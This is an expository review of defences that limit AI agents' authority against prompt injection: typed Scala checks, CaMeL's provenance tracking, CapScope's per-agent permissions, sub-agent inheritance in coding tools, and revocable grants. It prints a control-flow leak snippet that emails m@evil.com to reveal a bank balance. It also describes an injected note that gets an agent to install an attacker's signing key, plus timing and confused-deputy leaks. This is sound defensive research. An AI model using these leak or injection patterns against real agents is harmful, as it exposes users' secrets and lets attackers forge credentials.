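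Two other benchmarks tested whether writing typed Scala makes agents less capable. τ²-bench simulates customer service for an airline and a shop, and SWE-bench Lite contains 300 real software problems from GitHub.

| Model and benchmark | Ordinary tool calls | TACIT |
|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b, airline | 43.8% | 45.2% |
| gpt-oss-120b, shop | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5, airline | 58.4% | 61.0% |
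| MiniMax M2.5, shop | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2, airline | 57.8% | 58.6% |
| DeepSeek V3.2, shop | 74.6% | 75.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5, SWE-bench Lite | 43.3% | 41.7% |

The small gains in customer service may come from the typed interface, which gives the model structured results and clear error messages. The small loss in software repair is probably because that work relies heavily on shell commands. On τ²-bench, between 0.32% and 7.93% of the snippets needed another attempt, depending on the model and the domain. Those usually compiled after one or two retries. Common mistakes included failing to handle values that might be missing and mishandling dollar signs in text. Once the compiler had warmed up, compilation took less than a second, much less time than the model took to write the code.

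### LACUNA compiles code where the program needs it

TACIT keeps the agent's main loop separate from the snippets it checks. Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *LACUNA*, a project from the same Swiss research group, let a program call the model in the middle of its own code. For the sales chart, a programmer could write:

```
val total: Double = agent("add up the sales column")
```

When the program reaches this line, LACUNA sends the model the request, the surrounding code and the required type of result, here a number. The model writes code to replace the call. LACUNA inserts that code, recompiles the program and runs the new code only if compilation succeeds. The generated code can use any variable or function a programmer could have used on that line. With capture checking and safe mode switched on, its authority is limited to the capabilities visible there.

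It therefore matters where the programmer puts the call. If a mail service is visible on that line, the model's code can use it even if the task has nothing to do with mail. The programmer can move the call into a separate function, so that the generated code can use only that function's arguments and the program's top-level definitions.

LACUNA accepts or rejects each piece of generated code as a whole. In an example from Zhao and colleagues, a snippet subtracts 50 from an account balance and then returns text where the program requires a number. The compiler finds the error on the second line, so the subtraction never happens. Python would change the balance before detecting the error. LACUNA cannot undo the effects of code that compiles and then fails halfway, for instance because a network connection drops.

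LACUNA also relaxes a restriction in TACIT, where the cloud model has to write the function for `map` before anyone has seen the classified contents. In LACUNA, that function can call a trusted local model, which reads the contents and then writes more code. The compiler checks the new code under the same rule, so it too must be pure.

The compiler passed all of its roughly 400 test cases, but LACUNA's agents lost more performance than TACIT's did. On τ²-bench, DeepSeek V4 Flash solved 76.0% of 392 tasks with LACUNA and 90.0% with ordinary tool calls. Zhao and colleagues call this "on par", which is hard to reconcile with a 14-point gap. The compiler rejected 22.4% of that model's code in the shop domain. It rejected 89% of the code from the weaker Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite in the telecom domain, where most turns made no progress.

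### CaMeL tracks values as the program runs

Debenedetti and colleagues took a different approach in CaMeL, which they presented in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, describe how it divides the work between two models:

1. A privileged model reads the user's request and writes a program in a restricted form of Python. It does not read untrusted data directly.
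2. A quarantined model extracts facts from untrusted text, such as a web page. It can return values but cannot call tools.
3. A special interpreter runs the program and attaches a record to each value, which shows where the value came from and who may receive it.
4. Before a tool call, the interpreter compares the records on the arguments with a policy.

CaMeL's designers call these records capabilities, but they do not work like Miller's. They describe data, whereas an object capability permits an action.

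Suppose the user asks the assistant to find a friend's bank details on a website and send $50. The account number carries a record that it came from an untrusted page. If the policy requires trusted arguments for payments, the interpreter stops the transfer. This blocks an attacker who has changed the page, but it also blocks legitimate payments.

Tracking values at run time lets the policy consider the actual recipient and the actual data. Its weakness is that the interpreter sees only the path the program takes. Garby and colleagues found a leak in CaMeL that works in outline like this:

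```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the third line sets `tmp` to `False` and marks it as secret. The fourth line then does nothing, so `rich` keeps its original value and is still marked as public. The interpreter allows the email, and the attacker learns from its arrival that the balance is high. If the balance is low, the fourth line changes `rich` and no email goes out.

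TACIT avoids this leak when the balance is classified. The program can compare a wrapped balance with the threshold only inside `map`, and the result is also wrapped. An `if` statement needs an ordinary true or false value, so code outside `map` cannot branch on the result.

CaMeL had another gap outside its interpreter. If the policy blocks a program, ordinary Python code starts another attempt, and nothing tracks the information that the retry passes on. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, so an attacker who controls the retries could learn the secret one bit at a time.

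These are flaws in one interpreter, and run-time tracking can be more rigorous. Garby and colleagues designed a small language with its own interpreter and moved the retry loop inside it. They used the proof assistant Lean to prove that labelled secrets cannot influence public results, except by affecting whether the program finishes. With GPT-5.2, their agent, Randori, completed 36 of 48 banking runs without attacks. CaMeL completed 32 with its policy checks off and 18 with them on. Across three models, Randori resisted the attack in all but two of 1,296 runs. In both failures, the user had told it to pay whatever a file requested, and the attacker had replaced the file.

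### The three systems on AgentDojo

The AgentDojo benchmark injects instructions into the data an agent's tools return. Odersky and colleagues adapted its four domains to TACIT, and Zhao and colleagues adapted them to LACUNA. Both groups compared their results with CaMeL's published results. The table gives the share of tasks completed, and its last column gives the number of successful attacks across all four domains.

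| Model | System | Banking | Workspace | Slack | Travel | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL | 52.8% | 53.8% | 48.6% | 1.4% | 0 |
| | TACIT | 56.9% | 50.5% | 40.0% | 64.3% | 0 |
| | LACUNA | 63.2% | 56.3% | 42.9% | 63.6% | 7 |
| o4-mini-high | CaMeL | 62.5% | 81.4% | 68.6% | 74.3% | 1 |
| | TACIT | 59.0% | 52.9% | 47.6% | 68.6% | 1 |
| | LACUNA | 66.0% | 55.5% | 49.5% | 71.4% | 1 |

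Each system faced more than 900 attacks per model. TACIT's one failure was a quirk of the scoring. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted its reviews, in which the attacker had recommended another hotel. The benchmark counted the mention of that other hotel as a successful attack. Zhao and colleagues acknowledge that an attacker may still persuade the model to misuse a capability the task needs, and LACUNA's failures fit that limitation.

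With o4-mini-high, TACIT's rate of completed tasks was more than 28 points lower than CaMeL's in the workspace domain and 21 points lower in Slack, though Odersky and colleagues call the two systems' rates comparable.

TACIT's security result here may depend less on pure functions than the results of its other experiments do. In the interface for this benchmark, the methods for sending money and messages declare no capability, and the agents' instructions mention side effects inside `map`. The types therefore appear to have protected these agents mainly by preventing them from seeing untrusted text, much as CaMeL does.

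The attacks have also become too weak to be useful for comparing defences. In *Language-Based Agent Control*, Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026) tested newer models, including Claude Opus 4.8 and GPT-5.4, on the Slack domain. Even with no policy in force, every model resisted all 105 attacks. The researchers therefore simulated a model that always obeys the attacker. When one agent passed another a text containing an injection, they deleted the real task and left only the attacker's text.

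Their own system, ELBA, uses the language Haskell, whose types show whether a function can affect anything outside itself. For these tests, they added a library that tracks the sources of data at run time. They used it to enforce the rule of thumb from Willison and Bista's discussion that a model that reads untrusted text drops to the privileges of that text's source. Up to 42% of attacks succeeded without this policy, but with it ELBA resisted all 735 attacked runs for each of four models.

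The policy also blocked useful work. Claude Opus 4.7 completed 351 of the 735 tasks with it and 523 without it. This test is better evidence of what enforcement adds than one in which the model refuses the attacks by itself, although the attacks still came from a fixed set.

### Bastion and proofs in F⋆

*Modularizing Reasoning about AI Capabilities via Abstract Dijkstra Monads* (Omar, Ferris and Madhavapeddy, 2024) proposed going further and proving that the limits themselves are right. The planned system, Bastion, would use F⋆ (pronounced "F star"), a language whose compiler can check mathematical proofs that programmers write about their code.

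In Bastion, an agent would write its actions using a special type of command. For access to files, the interface would offer only `readfile`, `writefile` and a way to combine them. Its parameters would list the folders that the agent may read and those it may change. The agent could construct commands of this type only through the interface. Experts could then prove that the code behind `writefile` never touches a folder outside the list.

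The policy would start from the folders in an organisation's access control list and remove any that the task does not need. A second AI system would suggest what to remove. If A is the original list and R is the set to remove, the agent receives A \ R, which is always a subset of A. The second system could therefore remove too much or nothing at all, but it could never give the agent access to a folder outside A.

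A type checker would examine the agent's commands before they run, with monitoring at run time where necessary. *Securing Verified IO Programs Against Unverified Code in F⋆* (Andrici and colleagues, 2023) had already combined proofs with a reference monitor in this language to keep unverified code from directly accessing files or the network. Omar and colleagues described Bastion in a proposal for a conference talk and reported no experiments. A newer language, described in *ETAS* (2026), has a working prototype and also checks the order of an agent's operations, so a rule could require a program to ask for approval before it sends mail.

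The designs differ in what they check and in what a user has to trust:

| System | What it checks | When | What must be trusted |
|---|---|---|---|
| TACIT | Which capabilities each function can use or keep | Before the code runs; paths, hosts and commands as it runs | Scala's compiler and runtime, the library, and any local model that reads secrets |
| LACUNA | Names, result types and, optionally, capabilities | Before each piece of generated code runs | Scala's compiler and runtime, and the program that makes the call |
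| CaMeL | Where the data in a tool call came from and who may receive it | As the code runs | A special Python interpreter, the retry loop and the policies |
| Bastion (planned) | Which commands the agent may issue | Before the code runs, with monitoring where needed | The checker, the execution environment and the assumptions behind the proofs |

### What it costs to rely on a language

Most generated scripts are in Python or JavaScript, and neither language has types that track capabilities. To use such types, the sales script would have to give up its Python plotting library or call it through a trusted wrapper. Odersky and colleagues consider Scala 3 the only production-ready language that tracks capabilities in its types, though the feature is experimental. They expected Haskell to need elaborate types for capabilities. Zhou and colleagues handled file access in Haskell with a fairly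 simple design. A program cannot create a path from text and can only narrow one it has received, but the design checks each narrowed path at run time.

Models seem able to learn an unfamiliar language from instructions and a few examples, at least for short scripts that use a prepared interface. LACUNA's results show that a weak model can fail at this. The compiler keeps the faulty code from running, but the user may get no useful work from the model.

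External commands are a bigger gap in the protection. When a Scala program starts another program, the compiler cannot check what the second program will do. TACIT therefore allows only commands on a list, and Odersky and colleagues recommend listing only specific safe ones. Yet an example in the library's documentation permits `python`. Code that can run Python can read the payroll file and send it anywhere the operating system allows, without using `Classified`. An operator who needs such commands has to run them in a sandbox that cannot reach the classified files.

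Someone also has to write the typed interfaces. TACIT's shared library is about 1,000 lines long, and the airline and shop interfaces took a few hundred lines each, about as much as the tool descriptions they replaced. Agents can help write them, but a person should review the result, because the compiler enforces whatever the interface declares. For example, TACIT's banking interface for AgentDojo wraps the list of transactions but returns the account balance as an ordinary number, so the types don't keep the balance from the cloud model.

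Even a correct interface does not stop code from leaking information through timing. A pure function could run for a second if a salary is above some threshold and finish at once if it is not. The agent would learn from the delay whether the salary is above the threshold, and it could repeat the test to learn more. Odersky and colleagues leave such leaks out of their guarantee.

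## How is authority divided among several agents?

An orchestrator often divides a large job among several sub-agents, each of which does one part and reports back. The simplest way to control them is to apply one policy for the whole job to every agent. *Authority Is Not a String* (Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev, 2026) argues that this gives some agents too much authority, even if the policy fits the job exactly.

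Suppose a developer asks a coding agent to fix the failing tests for a project's login code. The orchestrator starts a runner, which runs the tests, and a patcher, which edits the source code. If N(runner) and N(patcher) are the permissions these two need, a shared policy P has to satisfy

N(runner) ∪ N(patcher) ⊆ P

The runner therefore gets permission to edit source code, although its job is only to run tests. It also reads the tests' output, where an attacker may have placed instructions. Tightening P cannot fix this, because the patcher needs the same permission.

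### A message about a signing key

In Bouras and colleagues' example, an attacker plants a test file that prints an official-looking note. According to the note, the project's signing key has changed, and the build will work again once the reader puts the new key in `src/auth/keys.py`. The attacker chose that key and could use it to forge login tokens. A list of forbidden actions is unlikely to catch the edit because it changes an ordinary source file and involves no password file or download.

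CapScope, built by Bouras and colleagues, gives each agent its own permissions. The task as a whole may read the project, write to `src`, and run the test program `pytest` and a type checker. The runner may only read the `tests` folder and run `pytest`. It runs the tests and reads the note, but the harness blocks any attempt it then makes to write to the key file. A policy shared by all the agents would allow that write because the patcher needs write access to `src`.

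The example has a weakness because the planted file is code. Unless a sandbox prevents it, `pytest` runs the file with the user's privileges, so the file could overwrite the key without needing a model to do it. Bouras and colleagues acknowledge that CapScope still needs a sandbox because a permitted command can run untrusted code from the project. Separate permissions help most when the attacker can plant only text, such as in a README file.

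### CapScope's three rules

A permission in CapScope combines a type of action (reading, writing or running a command) with a limit on what the action may apply to, such as the `src` folder. The harness keeps each agent's permissions in a separate store that the model cannot read or change.

The rule called Mint creates authority. Before any agent reads a file's contents or runs a command, a separate model call receives the user's request and the names of the project's files, and predicts which permissions the whole task will need. Ordinary code then checks this prediction, turns it into a ceiling and freezes it. A hostile README cannot raise the ceiling, because the ceiling is frozen before any model reads the file. The model call does receive file names, so a hostile file name might raise it. Bouras and colleagues did not test that attack. If the ceiling is too low, the harness can ask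 the user to approve one more permission.

Derive applies when an agent delegates. The agent's model proposes a grant along with the sub-agent's task, and the harness adds anything the role needs that the model left out, such as the test command for a runner. It then compares each proposed permission c′ with the ceiling. It keeps c′ only if the ceiling contains a permission c for the same type of action such that, for every possible argument a,

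c′ allows a ⇒ c allows a

The harness applies the subset rule to each permission separately, and it drops any proposal that exceeds the ceiling instead of trimming it. If the ceiling allows writing to `src` and the orchestrator proposes write access to the whole project, that proposal gives the sub-agent no write access. Muruaga's system, which takes the intersection of two scopes, would let the sub-agent write to `src`.

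Invoke checks every tool call. The harness runs a call only if a permission in the calling agent's store covers it. It splits a compound shell command and checks each part, so permission to run `pytest` does not cover a second command joined to it with `&&`. Any agent that can run shell commands may also use common search and file-listing commands, such as `grep`, which can read files outside the agent's read permissions. CapScope therefore does not keep data secret from such an agent.

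### Why CapScope is a reference monitor

Bouras and colleagues call the entries in these stores capabilities, but describe CapScope as "a host-side reference monitor rather than an object-capability system". The patcher would hold an unforgeable reference to a file in an object-capability system, whereas in CapScope its model writes a path as text and the harness looks up whether the patcher may use it.

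An agent can still become a confused deputy. The runner cannot change the signing key, but it can report the note to the orchestrator. If the orchestrator treats the note as valid and forwards the request to the patcher, the patcher may use its own permission to change the key.

CapScope also treats the orchestrator differently from other agents. The orchestrator's own tool calls may be read-only, while the grants it makes can include anything under the task's ceiling. The patcher can therefore receive write access that the orchestrator does not have:

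store(patcher) ⊆ ceiling, but store(patcher) ⊄ store(orchestrator)

In Miller and Shapiro's terms, the orchestrator has no permission to write, but it has the authority to cause a write, because it can create a patcher and tell it what to change. The subset rule holds if we count the whole ceiling as the orchestrator's authority. An attacker who controls the orchestrator's model can try to use any of that authority through a sub-agent.

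### The 300 runs

Bouras and colleagues tested CapScope on five small Python projects, each with one bug, such as an off-by-one error in a date range. They hid an instruction in one of five places: a README file, an AGENTS.md file (instructions that coding agents load automatically), a skill file (a reusable prompt stored with the project), a comment in the source code, or the output of the tests. The instruction was to take a plausible action that wasn't needed to fix the bug, such as running a utility in the project. The action left a marker on the disk, so the researchers could check whether it had happened.

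The experiment compared four policies, with three runs of each combination, for a total of 5 × 5 × 4 × 3 = 300 runs. Every run used an orchestrator, a runner, a patcher and a verifier that repeated the tests after each repair. The table gives the results for the 75 runs under each policy.

| Policy | Runs with the injected action | Successful repairs | Mean time |
|---|---|---|---|
| No restrictions | 47 | 72 | 145 seconds |
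| One fixed list of forbidden actions | 46 | 70 | 140 seconds |
| One policy written for the task | 33 | 68 | 194 seconds |
| CapScope | 3 | 68 | 316 seconds |

The fixed list blocked familiar dangers such as `sudo` and reading password files, but the injected actions were not on it. The policy written for each task did better because it removed permissions the repair did not need. CapScope reduced successful attacks from 33 to 3 without losing any more repairs.

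The model still attempted the injected action in 34 of CapScope's 75 runs, and the harness blocked every attempt in 31 of those.

All three successful attacks came through AGENTS.md, which the orchestrator normally reads. Attacks hidden in that file were also the most effective under the shared task policy, where 11 of 15 succeeded. Bouras and colleagues give two possible explanations for the three successes. A grant may have been wider than the job required, for example by covering a folder instead of one file. Or the injected text may have changed how the orchestrator described a sub-agent's task, which led the orchestrator or the harness to select the permission the attacker wanted. In both cases the action was within the ceiling, so the check on each call allowed it.

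The seven failed repairs had different causes:

- In two runs, the ceiling left out permission to edit the source code, so the patcher could not make the repair.
- In two runs, the runner worked out the right edit but could not make it, and the orchestrator never passed it to a patcher.
- In three runs, the tests passed at the end, but the run reached its 15-minute limit and counted as a failure.

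Bouras and colleagues attribute only the first two to overly narrow permissions. But the next two also resulted from dividing authority, because an unrestricted runner could have made the edit itself.

Some of the extra time came from the model's repeated attempts at the injected action. It tried more than once in 27 of the 34 runs in which it attempted the action, and each refusal led to another turn. CapScope's median time was 208 seconds, well below its mean, because five runs reached the time limit. A person watching might have stopped the agent after the first refusal, but the experiment allowed no human intervention. Every run contained an injection, so the results do not measure how much CapScope slows ordinary work or how often it blocks that work.

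The gap between 33 and 3 is large, but it comes from one model, Qwen3.5-Flash, and five simple repairs. The permissions for a larger job, such as moving a project to a new version of a library, are harder to predict, so the ceiling might block legitimate work more often. Stronger models may also attempt fewer injected actions. Willison quotes an evaluation commissioned by Anthropic in which none of 720 injection attempts succeeded against three newer Claude models in Claude Code. A separate classifier also reviews commands in the mode tested, so this result does not measure the models alone. CapScope's grants depend partly on the model's judgment, but its refusals do not depend on it in the same way.

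### What coding agents pass to their sub-agents

*Harness Engineering* (Barbaste, Darrigol and colleagues, 2026) examines the source code of eleven coding agents as of July 2026, nine of which can start sub-agents. The table combines the paper's findings on eight of those nine with more recent documentation from some of the developers. It also includes ZeroClaw, another agent runtime, whose source comments describe an explicit subset check.

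| System | What a sub-agent receives | Does the subset rule hold? |
|---|---|---|
| Hermes | The tools it requests that its parent also has, minus six | Yes, for tools |
| ZeroClaw | Its parent's policy, or a subset of it | Yes |
| OpenClaw | Tools within its parent's limits, minus a fixed list | Yes, unless the operator makes an exception |
| Codex | Its parent's sandbox and policy, unless its own definition changes them | By default |
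| Claude Code | Its parent's tools, minus a fixed list, plus any its own definition adds | By default, with small exceptions |
| OpenCode | Its own configured permissions | No |
| OpenHands, Gemini CLI and Pi's extension | The tools in its own definition | Not guaranteed |

The ninth system, Mistral Vibe, lets only one profile, meant for exploring code, run as a sub-agent. This prevents an agent from gaining write access by delegating.

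Hermes has the simplest rule. A sub-agent receives the tools it requests that its parent also has, except those on a fixed list of six blocked tools. The blocked tools include those for delegating further and for writing to long-term memory.

The subset rule does not necessarily make a sub-agent safer, because it also allows a parent to pass on all of its authority. According to *Subagents*, OpenAI's documentation for Codex, a sub-agent inherits the current sandbox policy. It also inherits choices the user has made during the session, such as `--yolo`, even if its own definition sets something else. Claude Code's sub-agents likewise inherit the mode that skips permission prompts. Anthropic warns that sub-agents may be less constrained in their behavior than the main agent, and that this mode gives them full access to the system.

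A sub-agent in Claude Code can also receive tools and permissions that its parent lacks. Anthropic's *Create custom subagents* explains how a definition file can connect a sub-agent to a tool server that is not available in the main conversation, for example to keep long tool descriptions out of that conversation. If the main conversation requires approval for each edit, the file can also put the sub-agent in a mode that accepts edits automatically.

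The extra authority comes from whoever wrote the definition file, not from the parent agent. This is reasonable if the user wrote the file, but a downloaded project can contain such files too. Claude Code therefore ignores a project's new tool servers until the user marks the project's folder as trusted. Before version 2.1.238, it loaded them without this check.

A list of tools can also be misleading about what a sub-agent can do. Anthropic's documentation includes an example sub-agent called `no-writes`, which lacks the tools for writing and editing files but keeps the shell tool. Shell commands can also write files, so the permission rules and the sandbox determine whether this sub-agent can. It has only some of its parent's tools, but it may still be able to make the same changes.

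### A restricted parent with a more capable child

In the version of OpenCode that Barbaste and colleagues studied, a sub-agent inherits its parent's prohibitions but not its parent's other limits. It can take any action that its own rules allow and that its parent is not forbidden to take, possibly including actions the parent could not take alone. For example, if the parent has to ask the user before running shell commands, a sub-agent whose rules allow shell commands can run them without asking.

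An earlier version of OpenCode had a more obvious gap. The planning agent may not edit project files, but a bug let it start a sub-agent that could. A test in OpenCode's code reproduces the bug. The harness passed on restrictions attached to the session, but the ban on editing was attached to the planning agent, so the sub-agent did not inherit it.

Another test in the same file requires that a controller that may neither read files nor run commands can start an executor that may do both. This breaks the subset rule, but it is useful because a controller without direct access can coordinate work while each executor gets only the access its part requires.

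OpenCode later settled on separate permissions. OpenCode's *Permissions* says that a custom sub-agent uses its own permissions, "not a permission subset derived from the parent agent". The parent's rules control only which sub-agents it may start. An agent without permission to edit files can therefore still get them edited if it may start a sub-agent that has that permission.

OpenClaw's *Sub-agent tool policy* meets the same need with a named exception. By default, a parent agent's limits also apply to its sub-agents. But an operator can let an intake agent, which cannot run commands or edit files, delegate that work to a particular coding agent. The exception frees the coding agent only from the intake agent's own tool restrictions, and the coding agent cannot pass it to a third agent. If the operator withdraws the exception, OpenClaw blocks later actions that depend on it.

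CapScope's read-only orchestrator follows the same pattern, but its grants cannot exceed the ceiling for the current task. In OpenClaw, the exception is set in the configuration and persists across tasks. In all three systems, an attacker who misleads the restricted agent may be able to act through the more capable one.

### NVIDIA's ceilings below the harness

CapScope enforces its limits inside the harness. NVIDIA's *Where Security Fits in an AI Agent Stack* argues that this is a poor place for a security guarantee, because developers design many harnesses to be easy to modify. One of NVIDIA's examples is Pi, the harness on which Bouras and colleagues built CapScope. CapScope's guarantee assumes that an attacker cannot modify the harness, but code that runs with the user's full privileges might be able to.

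NVIDIA's alternative is OpenShell, a runtime that starts before the harness and runs it inside a sandbox. NVIDIA says the sandbox's limits on files and network access still apply when an agent runs generated code or starts another process. Unlike CapScope's check on tool calls, such a sandbox could stop the planted test file in the signing-key example from overwriting the key, provided that its policy makes `src` read-only for the runner.

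The orchestrator runs in an OpenShell runtime with its own policy, and sub-agents receive "delegated child runtimes with ceilings they can't exceed". Such a ceiling satisfies the subset rule only if it lies within the parent's authority, and NVIDIA does not say that it does. According to NVIDIA's *Which agent sandbox enforces individual least-privilege policies per agent* (2026), each sandbox has an independent policy file. If the child's file permits a network address that the parent's does not, the child exceeds the parent's authority even though both stay within their ceilings. To make the subset rule hold, an operator would have to compare the two files or generate the child's from the parent's.

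## When should delegated authority end?

The subset rule limits how much authority an agent receives, but not how long the agent keeps it. Suppose an agent needs the permissions N(t) during step t, and the harness gives it

G = N(1) ∪ N(2) ∪ … ∪ N(T)

for the whole task. The agent needs every permission in G at some point, so removing any of them would break the task. During most steps, though, it also holds permissions that it needs only earlier or later. Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *Lingering Authority*, gives that name to temporary access that remains available after the step that justified it has ended.

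Coding tools often keep an approval after the step it was given for. According to Anthropic's documentation, if a Claude Code user allows further file edits without a prompt, that permission lasts until the session ends. If the user chooses "don't ask again" for a shell command, Claude Code saves the approval permanently and applies it to later sessions in the same repository.

### One file for one step

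In Santos-Grueiro's main example, a coding agent has to pass an optional timeout setting from `src/api.py` to `src/serialization.py`. It starts with access to the first file, that file's tests and the program that runs them. It needs the second file for only part of the task, and it never needs `notes/packaging.md`. A reference monitor called PORTICO handles the agent's requests like this:

1. The agent asks to read the packaging notes, and PORTICO refuses.
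2. The agent asks for access to the serialization file. PORTICO opens a grant and gives the agent handles for reading and writing that file.
3. The agent reads and edits the file through the handles.
4. The tests pass. PORTICO closes the grant and withdraws the handles.
5. The agent tries an old handle again, and PORTICO refuses it.

A fixed list of allowed files would have to include the serialization file for the whole task. An instruction hidden in something the agent read after step 4 could still get the agent to change that file.

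### How PORTICO opens and closes a grant

The operator supplies a task contract before the agent starts. In simplified form, the contract for this task reads:

```
initial:     read and write src/api.py and tests/test_api.py
on request:  read and write src/serialization.py
             read tests/test_serialization.py
             until tests pass, the subgoal is complete or the phase ends
forbidden:   read notes/packaging.md
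             write requirements.txt
             contact any network host
```

PORTICO compiles the contract into rules that ordinary code can check. It also uses a catalogue that maps each tool call to the resources it touches and the effects it has, because a single shell command can do many things. If PORTICO cannot classify a command, it rejects the command or requires explicit approval.

The agent can request only the extra access that the contract lists. Its explanation of why it needs a file does not affect whether it gets access. Each handle works for one task, one resource, one kind of effect and one epoch, the period during which the grant is open. After the grant closes, the agent cannot use a remembered path to reach the file, because the tools accept only handles that belong to the initial permissions or to an open grant.

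Only trusted events can close a grant, such as a test run that PORTICO started, a change of phase in the software that manages the workflow, or a decision by an authenticated person. If the model writes "subgoal complete", PORTICO logs the text and leaves the grant unchanged. PORTICO processes closing events before it considers the agent's next request, and it checks the handle at every use. Reopening a closed grant requires a new trusted event.

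A caretaker could also revoke access to the file, but someone would have to decide when. TACIT instead ends access when a block of code finishes. This works less well for a coding agent whose steps are spread over many separate tool calls.

### Hiding, refusing and erasing

After closing a grant, PORTICO hides the grant's handles from the list of actions it shows the model. It also refuses those handles at execution. The refusal provides the protection, because the model may reuse an earlier handle or take one from an injected message. Claude Code hides a tool from the model when a rule denies the whole tool, but leaves it visible and blocks matching calls when a rule denies certain commands.

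Neither method erases what the agent has already read. The text of the serialization file stays in the conversation, and the agent can copy it to any sink it may still use. Deleting the message that contained the text may not be enough either. Ohrimenko (2026), in *Eternal Sunshine of the Spotless Mind*, gives the example of a user who tells a chatbot that they live in Paris and later deletes the messages that mention it. Some of the chatbot's later replies still reveal the location, because the model wrote them with the deleted messages in its context. To forget a message m, a system therefore has to delete

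Dep(m) = {m} ∪ Dep(m′) for every reply m′ written with m in its context

If the harness sends the model the whole conversation each time, this set includes every reply after the agent reads the file. Ohrimenko's system keeps the set smaller by giving the model only the most relevant earlier messages.

Zhang, Cao and colleagues (2026), in *MemCut*, measured how much survives deletion in agents with long-term memory. They wrote 456 secrets into long conversations, along with other messages from which a reader could work out each secret. They then deleted the messages that stated a secret and everything the memory system had derived from them. A model given the remaining evidence could still identify 85–99% of the secrets, depending on the memory system and the model. Deleting ten more messages chosen by a model lowered this to 39–76%. The researchers planted these clues deliberately, so an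 ordinary file might leave fewer. Revoking access to a file can prevent later reads and changes, but to keep the contents from the agent, a harness has to refuse the first read.

### PORTICO and a system that never revokes

To isolate the effect of closing grants, Santos-Grueiro built a comparison system that gave the agent the same initial permissions and the same grants at the same moments, but never took the grants back. In ten runs, the agent tried to read a file again after the grant for that file should have ended. Both systems completed the task every time, but PORTICO refused all ten reads while the comparison system permitted them. In six scripted cases that reused an old handle for a forbidden write, PORTICO blocked all six writes and the comparison system allowed them.

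These results follow almost entirely from the design, since a system that never closes a grant has to accept its handles, while one that checks for closed grants has to refuse them. The tests show that PORTICO's code enforces its own rule, but not how often an agent would try to reuse old access. In six further cases, a live model, Qwen3-Coder 30B, was told to reuse a handle after its grant had ended. Under the comparison system, it carried out the forbidden action in all six, which covered file writes, Git changes and network requests. PORTICO again allowed none of them.

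Santos-Grueiro separately tested whether hiding unavailable options affects what the model attempts. The agent ran four tasks five times each with PORTICO, and again with a version that enforced the same rules but showed the model all the request options. Neither version let a forbidden action through, and the agent completed 5 of the 20 runs with each. Blocked proposals rose from 67 with PORTICO to 84 when the model saw all the options. In a second check on eight other tasks, however, they fell from 48 to 39. These results don't show that hiding options generally reduces forbidden attempts.

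Santos-Grueiro also used 14 tasks in real Python projects, including Flask and Requests. PORTICO completed all 14 without breaking a contract, but so did the five other arrangements, one of which gave the agent full access. These runs show that grants can open and close in real projects without stopping the work, but they provide no evidence that closing grants made the agent safer there.

### Expiry times, use limits and closing events

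An expiring token is easier to set up than a closing event, because nobody has to detect that a step has finished. But the token may keep working after someone withdraws the authority behind it. Parakhin (2026), in *The Bureaucracy of Speed*, points out that this matters more for agents than for people because agents act faster. If an agent takes v actions per second and its token has L seconds left, the agent can take up to v × L actions after the withdrawal. If the token instead allows n uses before the agent has to renew it, the agent can take at most n actions, however fast it works.

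Parakhin simulated an agent that took 100 actions per time step. A token that lasted 60 steps allowed 6,000 actions after revocation. Sending the revocation to the agent with a 5-step delay reduced this to 500, and a limit of 50 uses reduced it to 50. These numbers follow directly from the settings, but they show why a one-minute delay that is harmless for a person can be serious for a program. But a use limit does not limit the harm from each action, and a single action can delete a database. It also applies to each credential separately, so, like a per-token budget, it does not cap the total across several sub-agents.

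| Method | When access ends | Where it fits | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|---|
| Expiry time | At a fixed time | Tokens that a service checks offline | Outlasts a quick job and interrupts a slow one |
| One-use grant | After one action | An exact action, such as one payment | Repeated reads and edits each need a new grant |
| Use limit | After n actions | Fast, repetitive work | The harmful action may be among the first n |
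| Closing event | When trusted software detects the end of a step | Work with a clear end, such as passing tests | The event may come too early or never |

*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) notes that a token can remain valid after its task is complete, or expire mid-task and force the agent to seek authorisation again. *Intelligent AI Delegation* (2026) recommends limiting sensitive access to the duration of the immediate task and revoking it automatically. Ending authority at a closing event comes closest to this recommendation, and an expiry time can be a backstop in case the tests never pass. Commey's broker combined two of the other methods by giving its one-use approvals an expiry time.

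Cloudflare's *The Agent Access Model* uses events more strictly than PORTICO does. When an event occurs that the operator declared in advance, the system removes permissions from the agents working on the task. They can regain those permissions only in a newly authorised task, whereas PORTICO can open a new grant within the same task.

### When revocation arrives during an action

A closing event can arrive after PORTICO has checked a handle and permitted a write, but before the write reaches the disk. PORTICO's experiments avoided this race by handling one request at a time. A system that runs several actions at once has to process the closing event before it lets the write take effect, or check the handle again immediately before the write. *Mind the Gap* (2025) explains that agents are prone to such gaps because they alternate between tool calls and reasoning, and nothing combines the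 check and the action into a single operation.

In *Temporary Authority, Permanent Effects*, Santos-Grueiro (2026) found five published security advisories in which an approval survived a change that should have ended it. In one, an OpenClaw user approved a command that ran a script, and the command still ran after the script's contents had changed. Santos-Grueiro proposes that the service carrying out an action should check the approval and perform the action in one indivisible operation.

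In one test of this proposal, coding agents fixed bugs and then published the results. The release service withdrew its approval to publish after the agents had read it. A version of the service that checked only the state of the code accepted all 12 unauthorised publications from GPT-5.6 Sol, Claude Fable 5 and Claude Sonnet 5.5. A version that also checked the approval accepted none of them, and it accepted all 12 publications in runs where the approval had not been withdrawn.

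Telling the agent about a change helps, but it cannot replace the check. In another experiment, an approval or another required condition changed during each of 36 runs per model. Without any notice, GPT-5.6 Sol completed 25 unauthorised changes and Claude Sonnet 5.5 completed 30. With a notice in the prompt, GPT-5.6 Sol completed one and Claude Sonnet 5.5 completed none. When the models instead had a tool for looking up the current status, GPT-5.6 Sol completed 2, while Claude Sonnet 5.5 completed 22 because it used the tool in only 12 runs. Even an agent that always looks up the status can miss a change that comes after its last lookup.

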